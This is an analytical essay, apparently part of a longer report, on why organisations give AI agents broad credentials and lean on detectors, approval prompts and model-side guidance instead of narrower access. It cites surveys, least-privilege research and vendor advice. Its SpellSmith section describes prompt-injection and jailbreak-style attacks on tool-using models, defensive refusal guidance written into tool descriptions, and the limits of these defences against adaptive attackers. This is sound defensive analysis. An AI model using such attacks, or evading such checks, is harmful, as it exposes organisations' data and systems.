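Narrower access would have prevented the main harm in all five of the incidents described earlier, and in several of them it would have taken only a different token or database account. Companies nevertheless often leave an agent's access broad and add detectors, warnings or approval prompts. One explanation is that their security teams have no real choice. That argument has four premises:

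1. Developers give agents broad access because an agent's needs are hard to predict, credentials are coarse and narrow grants need upkeep.
2. Security teams often meet an agent only after people have started using it, or can't change it because it belongs to a vendor.
3. Taking access away at that point risks breaking useful work.
4. A team can add detectors and automated reviewers without redesigning the agent.

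If all four are true, it is understandable that a team would add a detector and leave the access alone. That doesn't mean the team had no choice, because a firmer option can be harder but still possible.

Much of the evidence comes from surveys that security companies ran or paid for. Independent work is scarce, and *AI Security Priorities*, a research agenda published in July 2026, still calls for someone to document how organisations handle agents' permissions.

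### What companies believe and what they do

Illumio, which sells software for containing breaches, surveyed 1,100 IT and security decision-makers in ten markets. *Illumio warns AI authority is outpacing security controls* (Lagonsin, 2026) reports that 69 per cent of them said limiting what AI can access matters more than trying to predict every threat. But when asked for their two main controls, only 25 per cent named an explicit definition of what an agent may do. *AI agent permissions are outrunning security* (Zorz, 2026) notes that this was the lowest share for any option. Sixty-two per cent agreed that they had deployed AI tools before setting up the right safeguards.

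These answers are less contradictory than they look. Respondents could name only two controls, so a company that defines its agents' permissions carefully might still have named two others. The options near the top were guardrails built into the AI, human oversight and containment from outside. The first two are best-effort defences, but containment can be an enforced limit, and people who chose it may well have done so because they believed access matters most. Illumio sells containment, which is a reason for caution. But only 27 per cent said that the most capable AI had made network segmentation (dividing a network so that a machine in one part can't reach the others) more important, and publishing a result so awkward for Illumio makes the survey a little more credible.

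For another survey, *Agents Without Guardrails*, the research firm Enterprise Management Associates (EMA) questioned 202 IT and security leaders at organisations with at least 1,000 employees. EMA prepared it for Cequence, which sells protection for AI agents. Of the respondents, 94 per cent were confident that their agents had no more access than they needed, but only 33 per cent gave new agents just the access their task required. News sites reported the survey in September 2026, some under the headline that agents had acted out of scope at 65 per cent of enterprises, but SecurityInfoWatch's *As Agentic AI Scales, Enterprises Face Gaps in Detection and Control* dates it to August.

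Both figures come from the same people, so at least 61 per cent of respondents (94 minus 33) were confident without applying least privilege to new agents. Sampling error in a survey of this size is about six or seven points, far too small to explain the gap. TechInformed notes, though, that the 94 per cent includes people who were only "somewhat" confident. Some respondents may also have trusted later reviews to remove excess access, since 38 per cent gave agents broad standing access and reviewed it periodically. In Infosecurity Magazine's *65% of Enterprises Have Seen AI Agents Act Out of Scope*, Christopher Steffen, who wrote the report, says the gap is "between what's written down and what's enforced".

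The 65 per cent figure combines 29 per cent who reported a measurable impact with 36 per cent who reported a near miss. In Illumio's survey, 76 per cent had seen at least one AI-related security issue or warning sign. In a study by Economist Enterprise, supported by the data security company Rubrik, 98 per cent had experienced a disruptive incident involving an agent, according to AAP. These figures depend heavily on the wording of the question, and none is a good estimate of how often agents misbehave. The gap between belief and practice seems more reliable, because in both surveys the same respondents answered about each.

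### Why developers grant broad access

*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes the developer's problem with a coding assistant connected to GitHub. With an older type of token that covers all of a user's repositories, the assistant can use about 40 tools, 16 of which can write. Summarising the open issues in one repository takes two read-only tools. A token limited to reading that repository would have stopped the attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated. But the user's next task might be to fix a failing build, which means writing code, and the one after that might involve a different repository. The user can either make a new token for each task or make one broad token and leave it in place.

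Software could try to predict which permissions to grant. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) describes a model that predicts which data users would let an agent see. Its high-confidence predictions were 94.4 per cent accurate, but its accuracy was 66.9 per cent for users with no record of earlier decisions. Even a perfect version would predict what people are willing to grant, which is often more than the task needs. The same study found that people gave agents too many permissions.

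Developers who know exactly what access an agent needs may still be unable to grant only that access, as Crane found with the Railway token. In Okta's *Survey* of enterprise software buyers, over-broad access was the second most common security concern, and Okta urges software vendors to move beyond "all-or-nothing" keys. MCP leaves authorisation to the application that hosts the model, whose controls can be just as coarse. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) reports that Claude Code and the coding assistant Cursor apply fairly detailed permissions to their built-in functions, but offer only choices such as "Allow Once" and "Always Allow" when the same function comes from an MCP server. A user who wanted to allow emails only to colleagues would have to find another way to do it.

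Narrow permissions also need upkeep. Shen and colleagues describe how permissions pile up on an MCP server because each new feature requests more access and nobody revokes it when the feature is removed. Lists of approved servers go out of date too. Cequence reports that, of the companies in EMA's survey that limited agents to an approved list of outside tools, 49 per cent had a dedicated team that regularly maintained and audited the list.

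This makes broad access understandable, but unpredictability probably explains less of it than developers suggest. Parkinson and colleagues cite a study in which 99.8 per cent of 447,000 GitHub workflows had more access than they needed. A workflow is a script that GitHub runs automatically, for instance to test new code. Its steps are mostly written in advance, so a developer could usually read it to work out what access it needs. Another analysis they cite found that accounts on several cloud services used 1 per cent of their permissions. Excess access mostly goes unused and causes no visible trouble, so nobody has a reason to remove it. Saltzer's old explanation, convenience, seems to fit these cases better than any difficulty specific to agents.

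There is also some evidence that developers don't always grant broad access. *Scanning the Harness* (Kapner, Soceanu and colleagues, 2026) examined 2,660 coding-agent set-ups in public GitHub repositories. It found broad permission to execute commands in 2.5 per cent of them, and broad advance approval of tools for a skill in 3.8 per cent. This is encouraging, but it only covers files that developers published. Those files don't show a token's scope, and developers can switch off approval prompts on their own machines whatever the repository recommends.

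### Agents that the security team meets late

Employees can now build an agent without a software team. Microsoft's *80% of Fortune 500 use active AI agents* (2026) reports that more than 80 per cent of the largest US companies use agents built with tools that require little or no programming, and that employees in many roles create them. A sales manager can connect one to the customer database in an afternoon without telling anyone in security.

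Security teams seem to know that their organisations have unsanctioned agents, but not where they are. In a survey by the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, 54 per cent of organisations reported between 1 and 100 unsanctioned agents. In Okta's *Global CISO Insights 2026* (2026), which covers more than 300 security executives, fewer than half could confidently say where their agents were, what they could access or what they were authorised to do. In Illumio's survey, 26 per cent of respondents said that an AI agent or tool had connected to systems without security approval, in which case the security team had no say in its design.

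The security team may have no say in how a vendor's agent is designed, even if it hears about the agent on the first day. Michael and Roesner note that CaMeL and FIDES, which separate the plan from untrusted text, both fix their security policies in the system's architecture. A company that builds its own agent could adopt one of these designs, but a customer who buys a finished product can't replace its planner.

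But a company can still control its own data when its security team arrives late or it buys from a vendor. As OpenAI divides the responsibilities for a vendor-run agent, the vendor looks after the service and keeps its customers apart, while the customer decides who may use the agent, which data and applications it can reach, and what authority it has. If the shop had bought its support agent, it would still have issued the database account. It could replace the administrator's credential with a narrower one without seeing the vendor's code, provided the product accepted it.

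Access is harder to restrict when an agent uses a person's login. Cloud Security Alliance's *Identity and Access Gaps in the Age of Autonomous AI* reports that most agents have no identity of their own and inherit existing permissions. If the sales manager's agent logs in as the sales manager, the database can't distinguish their requests, and any cut to the agent's access also cuts the manager's. The security team first has to give the agent a separate account, which requires knowing that the agent exists. The second premise therefore holds well for unregistered agents, but less well for those that a company knowingly bought or built.

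### Taking access away from a working agent

Raghu Nandakumara, an Illumio executive, told Zorz that companies find it hard to define what a new agent should be allowed to do, and don't want to disrupt the workflow that made it useful. So they plan to tighten its access once they understand it better, "but that day rarely comes". Meanwhile, people come to depend on the agent, and a mistake in the new permissions will stop somebody's work, whereas a successful attack may never happen.

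Delinea, which sells software for managing access, reports that 90 per cent of organisations press their security teams to loosen identity controls for AI. In the same survey, 59 per cent said they lacked viable alternatives to standing access, according to Security MEA's *90% of Firms Pressure Security Teams to Loosen AI Identity Controls*. Among Illumio's respondents, 56 per cent were willing to accept more cyber risk than a year earlier.

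People may work around a control that gets in their way. A participant in *From Chasing Ghosts to Missed Attacks* (2026), a study of security operations practitioners, described employees who forwarded company data to their private email accounts so they could use it with ChatGPT. The company's safeguards had arguably made things worse, since the data was now in places the company couldn't monitor. OpenAI's warning about less governed tools describes the same risk for agents.

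Many companies seem unwilling to interrupt an agent even when it breaks a rule they have set. In a Cloud Security Alliance survey, 38 per cent of respondents said they require human approval when an agent exceeds its defined scope, 24 per cent require a record of the action, and 11 per cent block it automatically, according to The Paypers' *CSA survey finds 82% of enterprises have unknown AI agents*.

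The fear of breaking things is reasonable, and the stronger architectures do complete fewer tasks, but that fear is a much weaker reason to keep access that nobody uses. If the cloud accounts that Parkinson and colleagues mention really used 1 per cent of their permissions, their owners could have removed most of the rest without anyone noticing. Logs can help to find what is safe to remove. The shop could record the support agent's queries for a month and then issue an account that covers only the tables it had read. A month in spring might miss a table that the agent needs for Christmas returns, so some queries would fail later. Somebody could fix those failures the same day, but nobody can undo the leak of a customer list. Past use is also a poor guide if an attacker or a malfunctioning model has already been using the excess access, so a person should review the list of tables before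 the shop issues the account.

Abandoned agents are an even easier case, because revoking the credentials of an agent that nobody runs can't break anybody's work. Cequence says that 31 per cent of agent pilots had been paused indefinitely, discontinued or abandoned, and that many left live credentials behind. The figure is probably a share of respondents, not of pilots, since TechInformed says that EMA asked what had happened to most of the pilots that didn't reach production.

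Companies could also avoid much of the problem by following OpenAI's suggestion to start with a clearly defined purpose and limited access, then expand as evidence accumulates that the limits work. Users then experience each change as a new ability instead of a loss. Deloitte similarly thinks oversight in general is likely to be slower and costlier to add later. This advice comes too late for agents that are already running, but companies can still apply it to new ones.

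### SpellSmith and guidance in place of a repair

The fourth premise is the easiest to support, because many best-effort defences were designed to work without changes to the agent or its tools. One example is SpellSmith, which Shi and colleagues built after studying vulnerable MCP servers.

Waiting for repairs is unattractive because the study found them large and slow, and a company that depends on somebody else's server can do little to hurry its maintainers. Fixed vulnerabilities took an average of 37.3 days from disclosure to repair, and unfixed ones had been public for an average of 92.3 days when the study ended. Maintainers treated 33 of the 53 vulnerabilities as a high priority, but for 9 others they replied without fixing anything, and for 3 they never replied.

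SpellSmith changes the instructions given to the model without changing the server's code. It first uses a tool's name, description and schema to estimate whether untrusted input could reach a sensitive operation, such as running a command. It then rewrites the description to state what the tool can do, which parameters an attacker might control, what kind of flaw might result, and which calls the model should refuse. For Markdownify's web page tool, the new description might tell the model not to fetch internal addresses. Finally, SpellSmith adds a review step in which the model checks, before each call, that the call suits the tool's purpose and that the user appears to have permission to make it.

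Shi and colleagues tested this on GPT-4o with 792 malicious prompts, based on the real vulnerabilities and ten known ways of talking a model out of its safety rules. The table shows the share of prompts for which at least one attempt succeeded:

| Text added to the tool description | Without the review step | With the review step |
| --- | --- | --- |
| None | 63.89% | 3.16% |
| General warning about this class of flaw | 28.41% | 1.52% |
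| Warning about the wrong flaw | 12.75% | 0.51% |
| Warning about the flaw SpellSmith identified | 9.09% | 0.13% |

The headline figure of 0.13 per cent is one prompt out of 792. Most of this very large improvement comes from the review step, which asks the model to think again. That step alone lowered the rate to 3.16 per cent, or 25 prompts, without changing any description.

In the third row, oddly, a warning about a flaw that the tool didn't have worked nearly as well as the correct one. With the review step, the difference was 4 prompts against 1, which could easily be chance. The warnings may therefore work mainly by making the model suspicious of the tool. A suspicious model might also refuse calls that it should make, and a model that refused every call would score 0 per cent. Shi and colleagues did not measure how often legitimate requests failed, which is a serious omission given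 how many ordinary tasks fail with some detectors.

The test shows that GPT-4o, with this guidance, resists nearly all prompts of the kinds that Shi and colleagues wrote. Even for similar prompts, one successful attack in 792 is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.7 per cent. The test didn't measure the success rate for an attacker who knows about the guidance and rewrites the prompt to get round it. Nasr and colleagues' results suggest that rate would be much higher, though a newer model might do better than GPT-4o.

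More fundamentally, the flaw is still in the server. The guidance affects only models that read it, so any other caller could exploit the server as before. SpellSmith also does not address tools that are dangerous without being faulty. For example, a warning in the description of `query_customers` would leave the administrator's credential in place.

SpellSmith makes sense as a stopgap for the weeks before a repair arrives. But a company that can't repair a server can usually choose where to run it. It could put Markdownify in a container (an isolated environment on the same machine) that has no route to the internal network. This would need no changes to the server's code and apply to every caller. Only 2 of the 41 repairs that Shi and colleagues examined relied on an isolated environment.

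Teams may not add a defence even if it is easy to add. Nearly all the practitioners in *From Chasing Ghosts to Missed Attacks* recommended letting a language model look up reference documents to reduce its errors, but only one reported doing so. Some also proposed further training for the same purpose, but none had done it. Best-effort defences also take time to install and test, which comparisons with firmer limits often leave out.

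### Whether a firmer option was available

Security teams can sometimes add an enforced limit without rebuilding the agent. The shop could move the original support agent to an account that can only read the orders table, which would protect the home addresses and prevent deletions. The model, its instructions and its tools would stay the same, and the change might take an hour. The shop could then add a gateway that releases an email only if the recipient has an open ticket.

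Even with these two changes, an attacker who opened a ticket could ask for other customers' orders, and the agent could read them and send them to the attacker. Until someone writes a narrower tool, such as a lookup restricted to the customer on the ticket, the shop has to rely on the model and its detectors to protect the order histories. It doesn't have to rely on them to protect the addresses or prevent the loss of the database. The shop therefore relies on best-effort defences partly out of necessity and partly by choice, and the balance depends on how much work it is willing to do.

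Commercial products show a similar split. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* covers 21 agent products on sale or in use in April 2026. Sixteen let people configure the agent's scope, 15 asked for approval at runtime and 14 supported written policies. None offered trust labels on data or checks that tie each action to the user's original intent, though these were among the methods researchers had studied most. The lack of commercial options in April was therefore a much better reason for going without something like FIDES than for leaving a product's scope settings unused.

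Companies gave employees permissions by role because nobody could issue new ones for every task. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) argues that this compromise is "no longer forced" for AI agents, even open-ended ones. Permissions are hardest to list in advance for these agents, such as one asked to find out why refunds have doubled. But an agent's task arrives as text that software can read, so the software can work out a set of permissions when it assigns the work and withhold every other credential.

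This is a good argument against giving an agent the same access all year. It is less convincing about how narrow the permissions can be, because a task description can omit important details, as the requests in Yang, Zhou and colleagues' tests did. Parkinson and colleagues also note that an estimate of what a task needs can be too narrow or too broad, and an investigation may change direction midway.

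Parkinson and colleagues propose to let access stretch and spring back. Each agent would have a small baseline of permissions and a larger "envelope" that its owner sets in advance. It could borrow permissions from the envelope for a limited time, paying for them out of a budget that refills gradually. The price would depend partly on power, with suggested weights of 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering. It would also rise as the agent approached a forbidden combination, such as the three properties in Meta's Rule of Two. If φ is the fraction of the combination that the session already has, the price is multiplied by

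s = 1 ÷ (1 − φ).

The multiplier is 1.5 with one of the three properties and 3 with two. With all three it would be infinite, so the software rejects the request. Ordinary code would issue the credentials and track how much of the budget has been used, so even a persuasive prompt injection could not make an agent exceed its budget.

The idea is attractive because setting an overall limit is easier for the owner than predicting each task. But the agent could still misuse any permission within that limit, and one read that uses little of it may be enough to leak a secret. Parkinson and colleagues present the scheme as a research agenda and leave open how well it would work. A company that needs a general-purpose agent today therefore has to accept some excess access and rely partly on judgement to control it.

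Detection would be useful even if the agent's access were perfectly restricted. The rebuilt support agent could still promise a customer a refund they aren't due, and database permissions wouldn't catch that. David C also recommends monitoring, but puts more weight on safeguards that limit what the system can do than on trying to keep malicious text away from the model. OpenAI says advisory checks, such as a reviewing model, should never be the only protection against something that must not happen automatically. By that standard, using a detector is fine, but the original support agent fails because only the model's good behaviour protects the customer database.

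### Who decides how much access an agent gets

A security team's choice of defence depends partly on what it has the authority to change. It can usually buy a detector from its own budget and install it in front of the agent. Changing the agent's database account may require the database team, and a narrower token may require a change by the vendor. If the shop wants the agent to stop handling refunds, somebody in charge of customer service has to agree. The detector needs the fewest approvals of these options, though it may offer the least protection.

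An agent may have no clear owner. In the Cloud Security Alliance's survey, only 15 per cent of respondents said more than three-quarters of their agents had a defined owner. Nandakumara thinks the business leader who approved an agent's use should own the outcome, while the head of security should own its guardrails, including what the agent can access and how quickly someone can stop it. When nobody else is named, security becomes the default owner of business decisions, which Nandakumara calls a mistake.

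This division is sensible, but it only works if the head of security can refuse requests for looser controls. In a company that presses for them, a head of security who formally owns an agent's access has the responsibility without much of the power. The security team may then be "forced" to rely on best-effort defences, but the company still has a choice, because its managers are the ones preventing the team from narrowing the agent's access and could change their minds at any time.

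Outside rules may push the decision back up to managers. Nandakumara says that the UK's senior managers regime and APRA, Australia's financial regulator, both expect a named person to be accountable for what AI does. OpenAI likewise says that whoever deployed an agent remains responsible for the outcome. A manager who is accountable for a leak has more reason to accept a few failed queries, though naming someone doesn't help if that person doesn't know what the agent can access.

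### The history of SQL injection

David C fears that prompt injection will follow the same course as SQL injection, because companies are adding language models to most of their applications before designing for the risk. In David C's account, people first described SQL injection in the 1990s, and attacks peaked around 2010, by which time databases were a core part of many websites but few sites had dealt with the risk. A decade of break-ins and leaks led to better defaults and better ways of writing queries, and the flaw is now rare in websites.

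Defenders had a choice with SQL injection. Parameterised queries were a complete technical remedy, and sites stayed vulnerable because their developers weren't using them. The history also suggests that the problem ended because the normal way of writing a query became the safe one, not because security teams were careful. That change protected even developers who had never thought about the attack.

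Prompt injection has no such remedy, so after another decade of breaches everyone might understand the danger and still have no fix. The comparison works better for access, because narrow tokens, read-only accounts and separate test databases already exist, and toolmakers could make them the default. A few have begun to, usually after an accident. Replit separated its development and production databases after its agent deleted Lemkin's records, and Railway began delaying deletions after PocketOS lost its data. These changes help security teams that arrive late, since an agent built with the defaults would already have less access when they found it.

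Safer defaults will probably be harder to keep for agents than for databases. A parameterised query gives a website's users the same results as an unsafe one, so hardly anyone has a reason to go back. A narrow token sometimes stops an agent from doing what its user wants, and the user can then replace it with a broad one, much as many Claude Code users switched off its prompts. Toolmakers can reduce the temptation by making it quick to add one missing permission, because many people will choose a token for everything if their only other option is one that is too narrow.
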